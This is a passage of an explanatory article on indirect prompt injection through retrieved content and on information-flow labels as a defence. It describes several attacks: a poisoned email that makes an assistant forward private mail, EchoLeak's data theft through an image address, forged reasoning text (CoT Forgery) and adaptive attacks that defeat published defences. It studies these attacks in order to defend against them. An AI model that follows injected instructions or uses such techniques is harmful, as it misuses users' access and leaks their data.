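# Prompt injection through retrieved content, and information-flow control as a defence

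## How does retrieved text come to override an LLM's instructions?

A large language model (LLM) is a program that continues a text one small piece at a time. Applications built on LLMs are vulnerable to prompt injection, in which the model follows instructions in text that it was supposed to read as data. In a direct injection, the attacker types the text into the application. In an indirect injection, the attacker plants the text in a web page, email or document that the application later fetches while working for someone else. For example, a person who asks an assistant to summarise a web page may get whatever the page's author wanted.

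One family of defences comes from information-flow control, an older branch of computer security. It labels every input with its source and arranges the labels in an order, called a lattice, that determines which data may influence which decisions. These labels are needed because of the route that text takes through an application.

### The prompt and the agent loop

The prompt an application sends to a model usually opens with system text (the developer's standing instructions) and continues with the user's request, any passages the application has retrieved, and the results of tools. A tool is software, such as a mailbox search, that the application runs when the model calls it. Each piece of the prompt has a role, which is the source the application attributes it to. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the initial prompt in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, as a list of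 items. Each item's role indicates how much weight its content should have, in descending order: system, developer, user, assistant (the model's own earlier output). Software then turns the list into tokens, which are integers that index into the model's vocabulary. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes the same step for agents in general, in which the conversation becomes a single prompt string.

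After that step, only the text itself distinguishes the sources. *Neural Exec* (Pasquini, Strohmeier and Troncoso, 2024) represents a prompt as Σ(κ₁, …, κₙ), where Σ is the fixed text of the developer's template and each κᵢ is a piece of outside data that fills one of its gaps. The model receives the finished string t and assigns a probability P(s | t) to each possible response s. Nothing in P(s | t) records which characters of t came from Σ and which from some κᵢ. Whether a sentence works as background or as a command therefore depends on its wording and the text around it. Developers add role tags to mark the source of the text that follows, but the model receives these as more tokens.

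Retrieved passages usually reach the prompt through retrieval-augmented generation (RAG), a technique that gives a model access to material it did not see in training. Pasquini and colleagues set out the usual procedure:

1. Software splits the documents into chunks, often at paragraph or sentence boundaries.
2. An embedding model converts each chunk into a vector, a list of numbers that represents its meaning, and a database stores the chunk with its vector.
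3. When a user asks a question, the same embedding model converts the question into a vector, and the database returns the k chunks whose vectors lie closest to it.
4. The application inserts those chunks into the prompt template beside the question.

The common measure of closeness is cosine similarity, sim(u, v) = u·v / (‖u‖‖v‖), which runs from −1 to 1 and is highest when two vectors point the same way. It measures topic, so a stranger's paragraph about a project can score as high as a colleague's.

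An agent application queries the model in a loop. Each time, the model outputs either a final answer or a request for a tool call, in a structure that software can parse. The model executes nothing itself, and Costa and colleagues stress that the application decides whether to carry out the request. If it does, it appends the result to the prompt and queries the model again, until the model produces a final answer. Bolin notes that in Codex the old prompt is an exact prefix of the new one, which saves computation. It also means that text from one tool result normally stays in the prompt for every later decision, unless the application shortens the history.

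### One email among many

Costa and colleagues illustrate the danger with an ordinary office task. A user asks an assistant to summarise recent emails about the progress of Project X and to send the summary to the user's manager. One of the emails comes from an outsider, and its text asks for another message in the mailbox to go to the outsider's own address. Step by step, the case runs like this:

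1. The application builds a prompt from the system text, the descriptions of the available tools and the user's request.
2. The model requests a mailbox search for Project X. The application runs the search, which returns several emails, including the outsider's.
3. The application appends the emails to the prompt as a tool result and queries the model again. The prompt now contains two requests to send something: the user's and the outsider's.
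4. If all goes well, the model writes the summary and requests one call to the email tool, addressed to the manager. If the injection works, it requests a second call that forwards the other message to the outsider.
5. The application receives both requests in the same format, each with a valid tool name and valid arguments. Unless some check intervenes, it sends both emails with the user's access rights.

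The attack works only if the search at step 2 returns the email and the model follows the email's instructions at step 4.

Many early experiments assumed that the malicious text would be retrieved. Researchers placed it in the "latest email" and had the user ask about the latest email, or they built a document collection with a single malicious text. Chang, Bao and colleagues (2026) tested retrieval separately in *Overcoming the Retrieval Barrier*, using 11 standard document collections and natural questions. Malicious text that nobody had adapted for retrieval never reached the top results. One would expect this from cosine similarity, since an order to forward a message is much less similar to a question about, say, travel expenses than genuine documents on travel expenses are.

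The barrier turned out to be weak. When Chang and colleagues added a short fragment fitted to the expected question, retrieval rose to nearly 100 per cent across the 11 collections and eight embedding models, for as little as $0.21 per question. The attacker did not need to know the other documents or have access to the embedding model's inner workings, but did have to anticipate the question. In the Project X case, an outsider who knows the project's name may only need to mention it.

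Chang and colleagues also tested the full attack. When a user asked for a summary of emails on a common topic, one poisoned email led a multi-agent system built on OpenAI's GPT-4o to leak SSH keys, the credentials for logging in to other computers, in about 80 per cent of trials. GPT-4o is now an old model, so that figure is a poor guide to how often a current one would follow the instructions in such an email. The retrieval result will stay relevant for longer, since it depends on the embedding model and not on the LLM.

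The security company Forcepoint ran a test closer to the running example. In *An Invisible HTML Payload Silently Hijacked Every Email Summarizer Run*, Gibney (2026) isolated a single email summariser, hid an instruction in an email's formatting code, and set the criteria for success before running harmless and injected emails through the system. The injection succeeded every time. The summariser had no guards, and Forcepoint sells protection against such attacks, so the result is best read as evidence about undefended pipelines.

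### From the user as attacker to the user as victim

The term "prompt injection" dates from 2022, when it typically described a user persuading a chatbot to ignore its instructions. Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023), in *Not what you've signed up for*, first set out the indirect form. They observed that earlier work had assumed the person prompting the model was its user, and asked what would happen if it was someone else. They demonstrated attacks on Bing's GPT-4-powered chat, on code-completion engines and on test applications of their own. In one attack, the chat assistant in the sidebar of Microsoft's browser followed instructions written in invisible text on the page the user had open.

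Greshake and colleagues distinguished passive delivery, in which the attacker leaves text on a public page for a search to find, from active delivery, in which the attacker sends it to a system that will process it. The Project X email is an active delivery. They also compared processing untrusted retrieved text to executing arbitrary code, since the text can determine which tools an application calls and how.

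Someone who injects a prompt directly works in his own session, usually with his own access rights, while an indirect attacker uses the access rights of another user, the victim. *A Layered Security Framework Against Prompt Injection in RAG-Based Chatbots* (2026) adds that a defence which inspects only the user's message will miss the indirect attack, and that one poisoned document can affect every user whose question retrieves it. An attacker can plant such a document without breaking in, because companies feed product reviews and support tickets into the collections behind their chatbots, and anyone can write a review.

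### The comparison with SQL injection

Prompt injection resembles SQL injection, an attack familiar to security engineers. Programs use the SQL language to query databases, and for nearly thirty years attackers have typed fragments of SQL into web forms. If a careless program pastes such a fragment into a query, the database runs it as part of the command. Parameterised queries prevent this. The program sends the command with empty slots and supplies the values separately, so the database never interprets a value as an instruction.

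In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published in December 2025, David C, technical director for platforms research at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, argued that comparing the two attacks is dangerous. He grants that they look alike on the surface, using the example of a system instructed to score a CV in which the candidate has hidden a line telling it to approve the CV. But a database engine handles commands and values differently, and parameterised queries work because they enforce this existing difference. An LLM has no such difference to enforce. In his words, "there is only ever 'next token'", so the model can treat text anywhere in its prompt as an instruction.

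He argues that detectors for suspicious text, training that teaches models to prefer the developer's instructions, and markers around the data all try to impose a distinction between instructions and data on a technology that lacks one. These defences can make an attack less likely to succeed, but he thinks it "very possible" that prompt injection will never be eliminated the way parameterised queries eliminate SQL injection. Gavish (2026), writing from inside a company that runs such products, similarly argues in *Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* that this is not a technical problem that one solves and leaves behind.

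David C prefers to describe the LLM as an "inherently confusable deputy". A confused deputy is a program that an outsider induces to use its privileges on the outsider's behalf. The Project X assistant fits this description because it can open the mailbox and the outsider cannot. Because the LLM is inherently confusable, he argues, designers should rely on deterministic safeguards outside the model that limit what the system can do. He also passes on a rule of thumb that while an LLM processes text from some party, its privileges should drop to that party's. The rule comes from an exchange between Baibhav Bista and Simon Willison, whose September 2022 blog post he links to for the origin of the term "prompt injection".

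His claim about the future, which he presents as a judgement, concerns what happens inside the model. The tool call at step 5 of the example, by contrast, has a name, a recipient and a body in separate fields, and ordinary software can refuse it on grounds the model cannot influence. Information-flow control places its boundary at the tool call.

### EchoLeak

EchoLeak, a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, is the best-documented case of this kind in a commercial product. Copilot is an assistant that can search a company's emails and files. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), an entry in the vulnerability catalogue of Spain's national cybersecurity institute, rates the flaw 9.3 out of 10 (critical) and describes it as a command injection that let an unauthorised attacker disclose information over a network.

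*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reconstructs the attack from the account of Aim Security, the company that discovered it. An outsider sent an employee an email. When the employee later asked Copilot a question about internal matters, Copilot retrieved the email along with internal documents and followed the instructions in the email. Its answer included a reference to an image whose web address contained the confidential data. The employee's software fetched the image automatically, which sent the data to the attacker without the employee clicking on anything.

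The attack got past three Microsoft safeguards: a classifier that looks for injected prompts, a filter that removes outside links from answers, and a browser policy that restricts where images may come from. The attacker also had to get the system to retrieve the malicious email. One way, according to TechRepublic's *First Known Zero-Click AI Exploit*, was to send a very long email, which the system would split into many chunks, each with its own chance of matching a question.

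Aim Security reported the flaw to Microsoft in January 2025. Microsoft fixed it on its own servers in May, and the details became public in June. Reddy and Gujral call EchoLeak the first known case in which a prompt injection caused concrete data theft in a production system, but the only recorded thefts were Aim Security's own demonstrations. Microsoft found no evidence that anyone else had used it.

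Two details matter for defences. First, Copilot could not send email by itself, so the data left through the answer on the screen, and a rule that monitored only the email tool would have missed it. Second, Microsoft's record in the GCVE database assigns the flaw to a class defined by a failure to neutralise "special elements", such as the characters that turn a value into a command in SQL. The EchoLeak email did not need special elements and read like normal business correspondence.

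### How common the attacks are

Google was one of two companies that reported in April 2026 on searches for injected prompts on the public web. *AI threats in the wild* describes its search of Common Crawl, an archive whose monthly snapshots hold two to three billion pages each. Google's researchers searched for well-known phrases, had Gemini judge each candidate's intent and its fit with the rest of the page, and reviewed what remained by hand. Most of the raw matches were articles about prompt injection. The genuine cases included pranks, notes meant to improve AI summaries, attempts to promote a business, and text meant to drive AI agents away. A small number aimed to steal data or delete files, and most of those looked like experiments by individual site owners. Repeated scans showed that the malicious category grew by 32 per cent between November 2025 and February 2026, but Google did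 not publish the number of pages behind that percentage. The archive leaves out most social media, and a search for known phrases misses unusual ones.

For *10 Indirect Prompt Injection Payloads Caught in the Wild*, Sewani of Forcepoint searched the company's data for four such phrases and examined ten live sites. One page contained complete instructions for a $5,000 payment. Another contained instructions for an AI system to refuse to discuss the page and to write a poem about corn. Sewani concludes that attackers are actively using the technique, and that the same template appearing on several sites suggests organised tooling. Ten pages, some of them jokes, are weak evidence for that. Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* reports that neither company found sophisticated, coordinated campaigns.

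In *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari, Zhang and colleagues (2026) analysed 1.2 billion URLs from 24.8 million hosts and validated 15,300 injected prompts on 11,700 pages, or roughly one URL in 100,000. A small number of templates accounted for most of the prompts, which fits Sewani's observation, but copying among site owners would produce the same pattern. About 70 per cent of the prompts were in parts of the page that a browser does not display.

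Khodayari and colleagues then tested whether models follow the injected instructions. In 5,200 controlled experiments with 13 models, compliance reached at most 8 per cent, among smaller models that received the page as plain text, and it was lower when the page kept its structure. This is far below Gibney's complete success, probably because site owners write generic text for any machine that reads the page, whereas Gibney wrote his for one undefended summariser. None of the three scans covers mailboxes, where an attacker targeting a particular victim would place an injection, so none would have found EchoLeak.

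### Integrity and confidentiality

Security engineers traditionally judge a system by whether it protects confidentiality, integrity and availability. *SoK* (Dehghantanha, 2026), a survey of attacks on agents, applies all three criteria to LLM agents. Availability means that the system keeps working. One site in Google's scan attacked it by luring AI readers to a page that never finished loading. Information-flow control concentrates on confidentiality and integrity.

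Integrity means protecting trusted decisions from untrusted data. In the Project X case, these decisions are which tools to call, how often, and with which recipient, and they should depend on what the user asked for. The outsider's email violates integrity when it causes a second call to the email tool, even if the forwarded message contains nothing confidential. The summary is harder to classify because the user wants it to depend on the emails, including those from outside the company. A rule that stopped untrusted text from influencing anything would make the task impossible.

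Confidentiality means protecting secret data from unauthorised readers. The user may read the whole mailbox and the manager may read the summary, but the outsider may read neither. Forwarding the message to the outsider therefore breaches confidentiality if its contents are private.

Integrity and confidentiality can fail separately. An email that puts a false figure in the summary damages integrity without revealing anything. Costa and colleagues point out that LLMs make mistakes even when all their data is trustworthy, and a model that misreads the manager's address can leak the summary without an attacker.

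For this reason, Costa and colleagues label data by both confidentiality and trustworthiness. In their examples, a search of a company database returns confidential, trusted data, and a search of the public web returns public, untrusted data. An inbox is more awkward because its contents are private, but anyone who knows the address can add to them.

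## Do role tags make a model keep instructions and data apart?

When the Project X assistant fetches an outsider's email, the application uses a role tag to mark the text as coming from a mailbox search. If the model reliably acted on the tag, it would treat everything in a tool result as material to read, and the outsider's request to forward a message would do no harm. Developers have trained models to behave this way for several years, with real but incomplete success.

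### Chat templates

A chat template is the format that puts role tags around each piece of the prompt. Providers such as OpenAI apply it automatically before the text reaches the model (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, *A Theory of Prompt Injection*, 2026). The tags are special tokens that a user of a hosted model cannot normally produce by typing. If someone types the characters of a tag, the software can split them into several ordinary tokens, so the model does not receive the real tag. An outsider who writes an email that the model reads can therefore imitate a tag but should not be able to insert one.

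Role tags began as a formatting trick. In 2020, a person who asked GPT-3 what one plus one equals might get another arithmetic question back, because the model continued the text. People learned to start lines with "User:" and "Assistant:", and the model, which had been trained on plenty of written dialogue, then supplied an answer. With ChatGPT in 2022, software began inserting the tags, and users could no longer edit them. Developers later added a tag for tool results and another for reasoning, the working text that some models write before they answer (also called a chain of thought).

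A new tag has no effect until the model is trained to use it. Standard chat training scores the model only on its own text, so it learns to write under the assistant tag and read under the user tag. This training alone doesn't teach the model to rank one source above the other.

### Methods that strengthen the boundary

In 2024 Wallace and colleagues at OpenAI proposed the instruction hierarchy, where system text outranks the user's messages, which outrank tool results. When a lower-ranked part of a prompt contained a conflicting instruction, they trained the model to answer as it would have without that instruction. This method changes the model's weights, the numbers that training adjusts, but not the prompt.

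Spotlighting, from Hines and colleagues at Microsoft in the same year, changes the prompt but not the model's weights. The application marks the text from one source and tells the model how to treat marked text. Descriptions differ on which source is marked. PYMNTS's *Anthropic Pushes Back as Hackers Press AI Weak Spots* reports that Microsoft uses the technique to isolate untrusted inputs, which matches the original proposal, while *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) describes marks around trusted text.

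StruQ, short for structured queries, also dates from 2024 and combines a stricter format with training. The application puts the instruction and the data in separate, marked parts of the prompt, and the model learns to ignore commands in the data part. He, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *PIPETTE*, write this kind of training, extended to agents, as the minimisation of

L(θ) = −E[ Σₜ log π_θ(aₜ | H′ₜ) ].

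H′ₜ is everything in the prompt at step t, including an injection, and aₜ is the action the original model took at that step when the injection was absent. π_θ(aₜ | H′ₜ) is the probability that the model with weights θ takes aₜ when given the contaminated prompt. Lowering L raises this probability. SecAlign, the successor to StruQ, uses preference training instead. Its training data pairs two responses to the same contaminated prompt, one that serves the user and one that obeys the injection, and training adjusts the weights to favour the first.

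Role embeddings mark the source of every token as it enters the model, whereas an ordinary template marks only the start and end of a passage. Normally, the word "forward" enters the model as the same vector, or embedding, whether the user or an outsider wrote it. Instructional Segment Embedding, from Wu and colleagues, adds a learned vector for the source to each token's embedding. ASIDE, from Zverev and colleagues, rotates the embeddings of data tokens by a right angle. No wording in an email can alter the added vector or the rotation, but the model's later layers can still learn to give the difference little weight.

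Training on roles can also teach a model shortcuts. Wang and colleagues found in 2025 that if each role always had the same kind of task in the fine-tuning examples, a model could learn to rely on cues such as where text stood in the prompt. Its scores would then improve without it getting any better at telling who wrote what.

### Measuring the role a model assigns to text

A model that refuses an injected command might have registered that the command came from a web page, or it might have recognised a familiar kind of attack. Recognising known attacks gives little protection against new ones. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) looked inside models to find out which of the two happens.

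The researchers used linear probes, which are simple classifiers that predict a property from a model's internal activations. They took neutral text from web collections, wrapped identical passages in each of five role tags (system, user, reasoning, assistant and tool), and trained a probe to identify the surrounding tag from each token's activations. Because only the tag varied, the probe could not rely on writing style, as it could have with ordinary conversations, where text under the user tag usually also sounds like a user. They trained each model's probes on 1,250 sequences of text.

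The probe takes the activations hₜ of a token t and gives a probability for each role. The token's "CoTness" is the probability of the reasoning role, P(reasoning | hₜ), and its "Userness" and "Toolness" are the probabilities of the user and tool roles.

The researchers first applied the probes to a short conversation about gardening with gpt-oss-20b, an open model from OpenAI. With the correct tags in place, the model's reasoning averaged 85 per cent CoTness, against 3 per cent for the user's text and 5 per cent for the assistant's. The probes had learned only the effect of tags, so CoTness should have collapsed when the researchers removed all the tags, but the reasoning still averaged 83 per cent. When they wrapped the whole conversation in user tags, the reasoning stayed at 85 per cent CoTness and reached only 2 per cent Userness, because its style overrode the tag.

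The result most relevant to retrieved content comes from Ye and colleagues, who ran 200 real conversations through four open models. They put text written by users inside tool tags, where an injected command in an email would sit. The text's Userness stayed between 76 and 88 per cent, depending on the model, and its Toolness never exceeded 20 per cent.

### From role confusion to successful attacks

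Ye and colleagues call this mismatch role confusion and tested whether attackers can exploit it. Their attack, CoT Forgery, adds a forged passage to a user's message or a tool result. The passage is written in the style of the model's own reasoning and ends with the conclusion that the model should comply. They tested the attack on six OpenAI models, using the 313 harmful requests in StrongREJECT. Plain requests and standard jailbreaks (attempts by a user to get forbidden help) succeeded at most 4 per cent of the time. With forged reasoning, success exceeded 80 per cent on o4-mini and the two gpt-oss models and ranged from 17 to 52 per cent on the three GPT-5 models.

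The attack's success depended much more on the style of the forged reasoning than on its argument. Absurd justifications, such as one based on the colour of the user's shirt, worked 60 per cent of the time, and plausible ones 63 per cent. When another model rephrased the forgeries to keep the argument but remove the typical wording of the target's reasoning, success fell from 61 to 10 per cent and average CoTness fell from 79 to 29 per cent. The models' genuine reasoning averaged 68 per cent, lower than the original forgeries. Across 626 attempts with and without the style, the group with the lowest CoTness succeeded 9 per cent of the time and the group with the highest 90 per cent.

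They also attacked an agent that had a file of secrets and was asked to summarise a web page. A plain injected command to upload the file worked at most 2 per cent of the time on most models and 26 per cent of the time on gpt-oss-20b. Forged reasoning raised the success rate to between 56 and 70 per cent.

In a test closer to the usual injection, Ye and colleagues wrapped one fixed command in 212 different framings. Framings that stated outright that the following text came from the user made up 24 per cent of the set but all of the top 5 per cent by Userness. In 1,000 attempts, the command succeeded 2 per cent of the time in the group with the lowest Userness and 70 per cent in the group with the highest. Success also rose with Userness among framings that claimed the same role, which makes it less likely that the command succeeded merely because the claim sounded persuasive.

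A separate experiment shows how strongly plain words can act as tags. Zhu, Li and Liu (2026), in *Discourse-Role Labels as Presentation-Time Variables for Context Use in Large Language Models*, gave GPT-5.5 a set of 500 multiple-choice questions, each with an assertion of a wrong answer. The model gave that answer 95.6 per cent of the time when "Instruction:" preceded the assertion, and 11.4 per cent of the time when "Example:" preceded the same assertion. The effect nearly vanished on arithmetic problems that the model had to work through. Zhu and colleagues did not test attacks, but anyone who can write an email can include the "Instruction:" label in it.

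The probe results come from only four open models with between 20 and 120 billion parameters, which are small by current standards. A linear probe also finds only one direction in a model's activations, so the model might carry the true tag in another form that the probe misses. However, the probe scores are closely related to successful attacks, which suggests that the tested models make little use of any such record.

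Ye and colleagues conclude that current defences rely on memorised attacks and that lasting protection needs models that recognise the true role of text. They add in their essay that the leading closed models can now mostly resist CoT Forgery. They think these models have learned to distrust text that sounds like reasoning, which could make them distrust their own reasoning. The essay includes no probe measurements for the closed models, so this explanation remains a conjecture. Memorisation alone could in principle make a model hard to attack if its training covered enough cases.

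### The adaptive-attack study

By 2025, many published defences reported that almost no attacks got through. Nasr and colleagues, whose group included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, suspected that the tests were too easy. Most tests replayed a fixed list of known attacks or ran a general attack program not adjusted to the defence. Evaluators in computer security, however, assume that the attacker knows how the defence works and has time to develop an adaptive attack, meaning one revised to get around that defence.

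The group chose twelve defences and attacked each with methods suited to it. Each method repeatedly produced candidate texts, tried them against the defended system, and used the results to produce better ones. One method trained a second LLM by reinforcement learning, rewarding it for successful attacks. Another used a genetic search, in which an LLM rewrote the best candidates, and a third used the defended model's gradients, which indicate how a change to the input would alter the output. The group also held an online competition with more than 500 human participants. The researchers set no tight limit on computing power because they wanted to know whether a defence could be beaten, not how much computing power that would take.

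Most attacks succeeded more than 90 per cent of the time. The results for the methods described above were among the worst:

| Defence | What it changes | Fixed attacks | Adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | marks in the prompt | as low as 1% | above 95% |
| Prompt sandwiching | repeats the user's request after the data | as low as 1% | above 95% |
| Meta SecAlign | weights, by preference training | 2% | 96% |
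| StruQ | prompt format and weights | near zero | every case tested |

The figures for spotlighting, sandwiching and Meta SecAlign (a version of SecAlign for agents) come from AgentDojo, a set of simulated office tasks with planted injections. The StruQ test measured only whether an attacker could make the model print a specific phrase. Many of the successful attacks on trained models imitated system text, as we would expect from role confusion. Others presented the attacker's task as a necessary step towards the user's, so repeating the user's request did not help.

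Filters did little better. Attacks found by search got past three of the four detectors more than 90 per cent of the time and past PIGuard 71 per cent of the time. MELON runs the agent a second time without the user's request and looks for tool calls that still occur. An attacker who knew nothing about MELON beat it 76 per cent of the time, and one who knew about it succeeded 95 per cent of the time. Two of the twelve defences, RPO and Circuit Breakers, were mainly meant to stop jailbreaks, and they also failed.

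The earlier tests were misleading because they used attacks similar to those the defences were built on. A model trained on known injections scores well when tested on known injections, but that is weak evidence that it will resist new ones. Tests that use automated attacks can also overstate a defence's strength. On a subset of scenarios, automated search succeeded in 69 per cent of cases, while human participants collectively succeeded in all of them.

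Nasr and colleagues warn against comparing attack success rates across defences, because they did not test them all on the same benchmarks. Several attacks also relied on more feedback than an outsider sending one email would get, such as a detector's confidence score. The study shows that none of the twelve defences was reliable against a determined attacker, but not that an ordinary attacker would succeed 95 per cent of the time. The models have also changed since the study.

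### How much training helps in 2026

Developers now publish tests in which the attacker may try repeatedly. Schneier (2026), in *Anthropic's Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection*, quotes results from Anthropic's July system card, the document that accompanies a model's release. The results are from the security firm Gray Swan's benchmark of indirect injections, which has 1,130 attacks in 28 scenarios, according to The Space Lab's *Claude Opus 5 Just Crushed AI Prompt Injection Attacks* (2026).

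| Model | Attacker succeeds within 15 attempts |
|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.0% |
| Claude Mythos 5 | 2.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 5.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 5.9% |
| Muse Spark (Meta) | 16.5% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol (OpenAI) | 20.0% |
| GPT-5.5 (OpenAI) | 20.8% |

On a single attempt, Opus 5 failed 0.2 per cent of the time and Opus 4.8 failed 0.5 per cent of the time. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5, released in September, reports results similar to or better than those of Opus 5 on every injection test. The developer published these results itself, but the differences between models are too large to be due to chance, and they suggest that training makes a substantial difference.

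Prompt injection is much more likely to succeed when an attacker can try repeatedly. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* describes an older Gray Swan test of that model in which strong attacks succeeded 4.7 per cent of the time with one attempt, 33.6 per cent with ten and 63 per cent with 100. If every attempt succeeded independently with probability p, an attacker with k attempts would succeed with probability 1 − (1 − p)ᵏ. With p at 4.7 per cent, that gives about 38 per cent for ten attempts and over 99 per cent for 100. The measured rates are lower because real attempts are not independent, probably since nearly every attack fails in some scenarios.

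Results also vary with the environment the agent works in. VentureBeat reports that Claude Opus 4.6 withstood all 200 attempts in a restricted coding environment. When the same model used a graphical interface, a single attempt succeeded 17.8 per cent of the time, and by the 200th attempt the rate had reached 78.6 per cent. Additional safeguards lowered that to 57.1 per cent. The Space Lab reports that attacks on Opus 5 in a browser succeeded 3.7 per cent of the time without safeguards and never succeeded across 129 scenarios with them. Those safeguards include a scan of what the model reads and a separate classifier that reviews risky actions, so the zero measures the whole product rather than the model's ability to separate roles.

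OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) describes a model built to find successful injections, which the company then uses to train its public models. The attacker trains together with a group of defending models, so the attacks get harder as the defenders improve. The Hacker News' *OpenAI's GPT-Red Automates Prompt Injection Testing to Harden GPT-5.6 Sol* (2026) reports OpenAI's claim that GPT-5.6 Sol failed six times less often than GPT-5.5 on a benchmark of direct injections. On Gray Swan's indirect benchmark, however, the two models were almost level, at 20.0 and 20.8 per cent, so progress against one kind of attack evidently need not carry over to another. Cross's *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense* (2026) reports a similar gap in OpenAI's figures for the later GPT-6 Sol, with 99.99 per cent robustness to direct injections and 97.13 per cent to indirect ones.

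Willison describes two tests from outside the laboratories. In an evaluation that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs, none of 720 attempts across 72 scenarios succeeded against three Claude models with safeguards on. In a public challenge, participants sent emails to an assistant running on Opus 4.6 to make it reveal a secret, and about 6,000 attempts failed. The challenge is much closer to the Project X case than most benchmarks are. The result is good for the model, but an attacker with a better method might still have got through. Willison wants more independent confirmation and still advises against relying on the model where an injection could do irreversible damage.

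PromptArmor, a company that assesses AI security risks for businesses, claims in *FrontierBreach*, its benchmark of long office tasks, to have found successful attacks on every provider's leading models. PromptArmor has a commercial interest in finding such attacks, and Anthropic has one in reporting none. There is also a newer reason to be cautious about test results in general. Suspicion of being tested appeared more often in the output of Anthropic's Fable 5.2 and Mythos 5.2, released in November 2026, than in that of any other recent Claude model, according to Help Net Security's *Claude Mythos 5.2 arrives with stronger bug hunting and less sandbox-breaking behavior* (2026). Anthropic acknowledges that this makes the two models' behaviour in real use harder to predict.

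### When more training attacks do not help

In November 2026, He and colleagues tested whether a larger collection of successful attacks produces a safer model. They used two automated attackers, PISmith and RL-Hammer, and two small open models. On one of these models, Qwen3-4B, PISmith succeeded on 68.75 per cent of 560 practice tasks and collected 7,132 successful injections, while RL-Hammer succeeded on 33.39 per cent and collected 4,282. They then trained a copy of the model on each collection and attacked both copies with three methods that neither had been trained on.

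After reinforcement learning, the strongest of the three attacks succeeded in 47.5 per cent of cases against the copy trained on the larger collection, compared with 27.5 per cent against the other copy. The larger collection also gave the worse result in two of the three remaining comparisons, which covered the second model and a different training method.

But the test had only 40 tasks, so each task counts for 2.5 percentage points. The large gap is 19 hijacked tasks against 11, and the other three gaps are one or two tasks each. Zorz (2026), in *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection*, adds that the researchers picked tasks on which simple attacks already worked against the unprotected Qwen3-4B. The study gives good reason to doubt that more attacks always help, but it does not show that they usually hurt.

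He and colleagues suspect that the attacks used in training are too repetitive. An attacker that earns a reward for each success tends to find one trick, such as claiming that the user's task is already complete, and reword it thousands of times. The model then learns to resist that trick. To counter this, their system, PIPETTE, rewards the attacker for successful attacks that use a new strategy. Attackers who revised their text over about 250 attempts still hijacked models trained this way on up to 10 per cent of the 40 tasks.

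Training can also make a model less useful. When the researchers trained Llama-3.1-8B on clean actions, as StruQ does, the share of harmless tasks it completed fell from about 40 to about 16 per cent. One likely reason is that the model learned to give up whenever ordinary data contained a sentence that sounded like a command, as office email often does.

### Tags inside the prompt and labels outside it

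A role tag and an information-flow label can record the same fact, such as that a text came from an outsider's email, but they take effect in different places. The tag is part of the prompt, where other words can outweigh it. Better training makes this less common, and the rates above measure how often it still happens.

The application keeps the label in its own memory, beside the value it describes, and ordinary code checks it when the model requests a tool call. Suppose the model mistakes the outsider's text for the user's and requests a call to forward the message. If the policy forbids untrusted text from choosing a recipient, the code refuses the call, and nothing written in the email can change the label. The application must still decide how to label the model's request. Because the model processes the user's text and the outsider's as one stream, any part of its output may depend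 on either, so a cautious application has to treat all of the output as untrusted.

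## What does a lattice of input roles allow and forbid?

The Project X assistant has permission to read the mailbox and send email. Checking each permission separately would therefore allow both the summary for the manager and the private message for the outsider. The two calls differ in where their contents came from and who chose the recipient. Computer scientists developed rules for this kind of problem in the 1970s, mainly for military computers, and current defences for LLM agents reuse them.

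### Denning's lattice of labels

Denning (1976), in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, observed that most access controls checked immediate access to a file but not where its contents could go afterwards. Her model gives every file, variable and user a security class, which later authors call a label. She writes A → B (later authors write A ⊑ B) when information labelled A may flow to a place labelled B. Information flows whenever one value affects another, so summarising an email is a flow, just as copying it is. A system is secure if no sequence of operations can produce a flow that this relation forbids.

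Denning argued that any consistent relation of this kind must be a partial order, which means that it has three properties:

- A ⊑ A, since assigning a value to itself is harmless.
- If A ⊑ B and B ⊑ C, then A ⊑ C. Otherwise a program could do in two permitted steps what it may not do in one.
- If A ⊑ B and B ⊑ A, then A and B are the same label, since anything could move freely between them and one of the two would be redundant.

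When a program combines values a and b, labelled A and B, the result needs a label too. This is the join, A ⊔ B, the lowest label to which both A and B may flow. The join must be at or above both labels because otherwise a program could send a + b somewhere that a alone may not go, and reveal a by setting b to zero. No higher label is needed, because a and b can be combined anywhere that may receive both. A finite set of labels with a bottom label and a join for every pair forms a lattice.

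In Denning's model, the join does not depend on which function combines the values. She made this assumption to avoid ambiguity when two different functions can produce the same values. It also makes the method usable with LLMs, because an application can label a model's output without knowing how the model arrived at it.

### Biba's model of integrity

Denning's main examples concern secrets. Kenneth Biba applied a similar order to integrity in MITRE's *Integrity Considerations for Secure Computer Systems* (1977), a report for the US Air Force. His example is a database of interstate transport routes. Many unimportant programs read it, but military logistics would depend on it in a national emergency. Everyone should be able to read the database but hardly anyone should be able to change it, and no single security level can express both requirements. Biba therefore gave data a separate integrity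 level, based on the damage that tampering could cause.

One of his policies, the low-water mark, lowers a program's integrity level to that of the least trusted object it has read. When a program s reads an object o, its new level is

i′(s) = min(i(s), i(o)),

and it may then modify only objects at or below that level. Biba proved that if information travels from one object to another through any chain of programs, the last object's integrity level is no higher than the first's. His levels rise with trust, so he takes a minimum. Most work on LLM agents puts trusted data at the bottom and takes a join, which is the same rule upside down.

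Biba also described a ring policy, in which a program may read anything and keep its integrity level. According to lecture slides from Purdue University, this policy assumes that programs process their inputs correctly, whereas the low-water mark assumes that a program may be contaminated by what it reads. The low-water mark is clearly the better fit for an LLM that might obey instructions in an email. But even that policy assumes that the program introduces no low-integrity information of its own, and LLMs sometimes invent facts.

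Biba recognised that, under the low-water mark, a program can "sabotage (inadvertently) its own processing" by reading something that lowers its level, and can recover only by starting again. In LLM agents this problem is called label creep.

### Coercions between four roles

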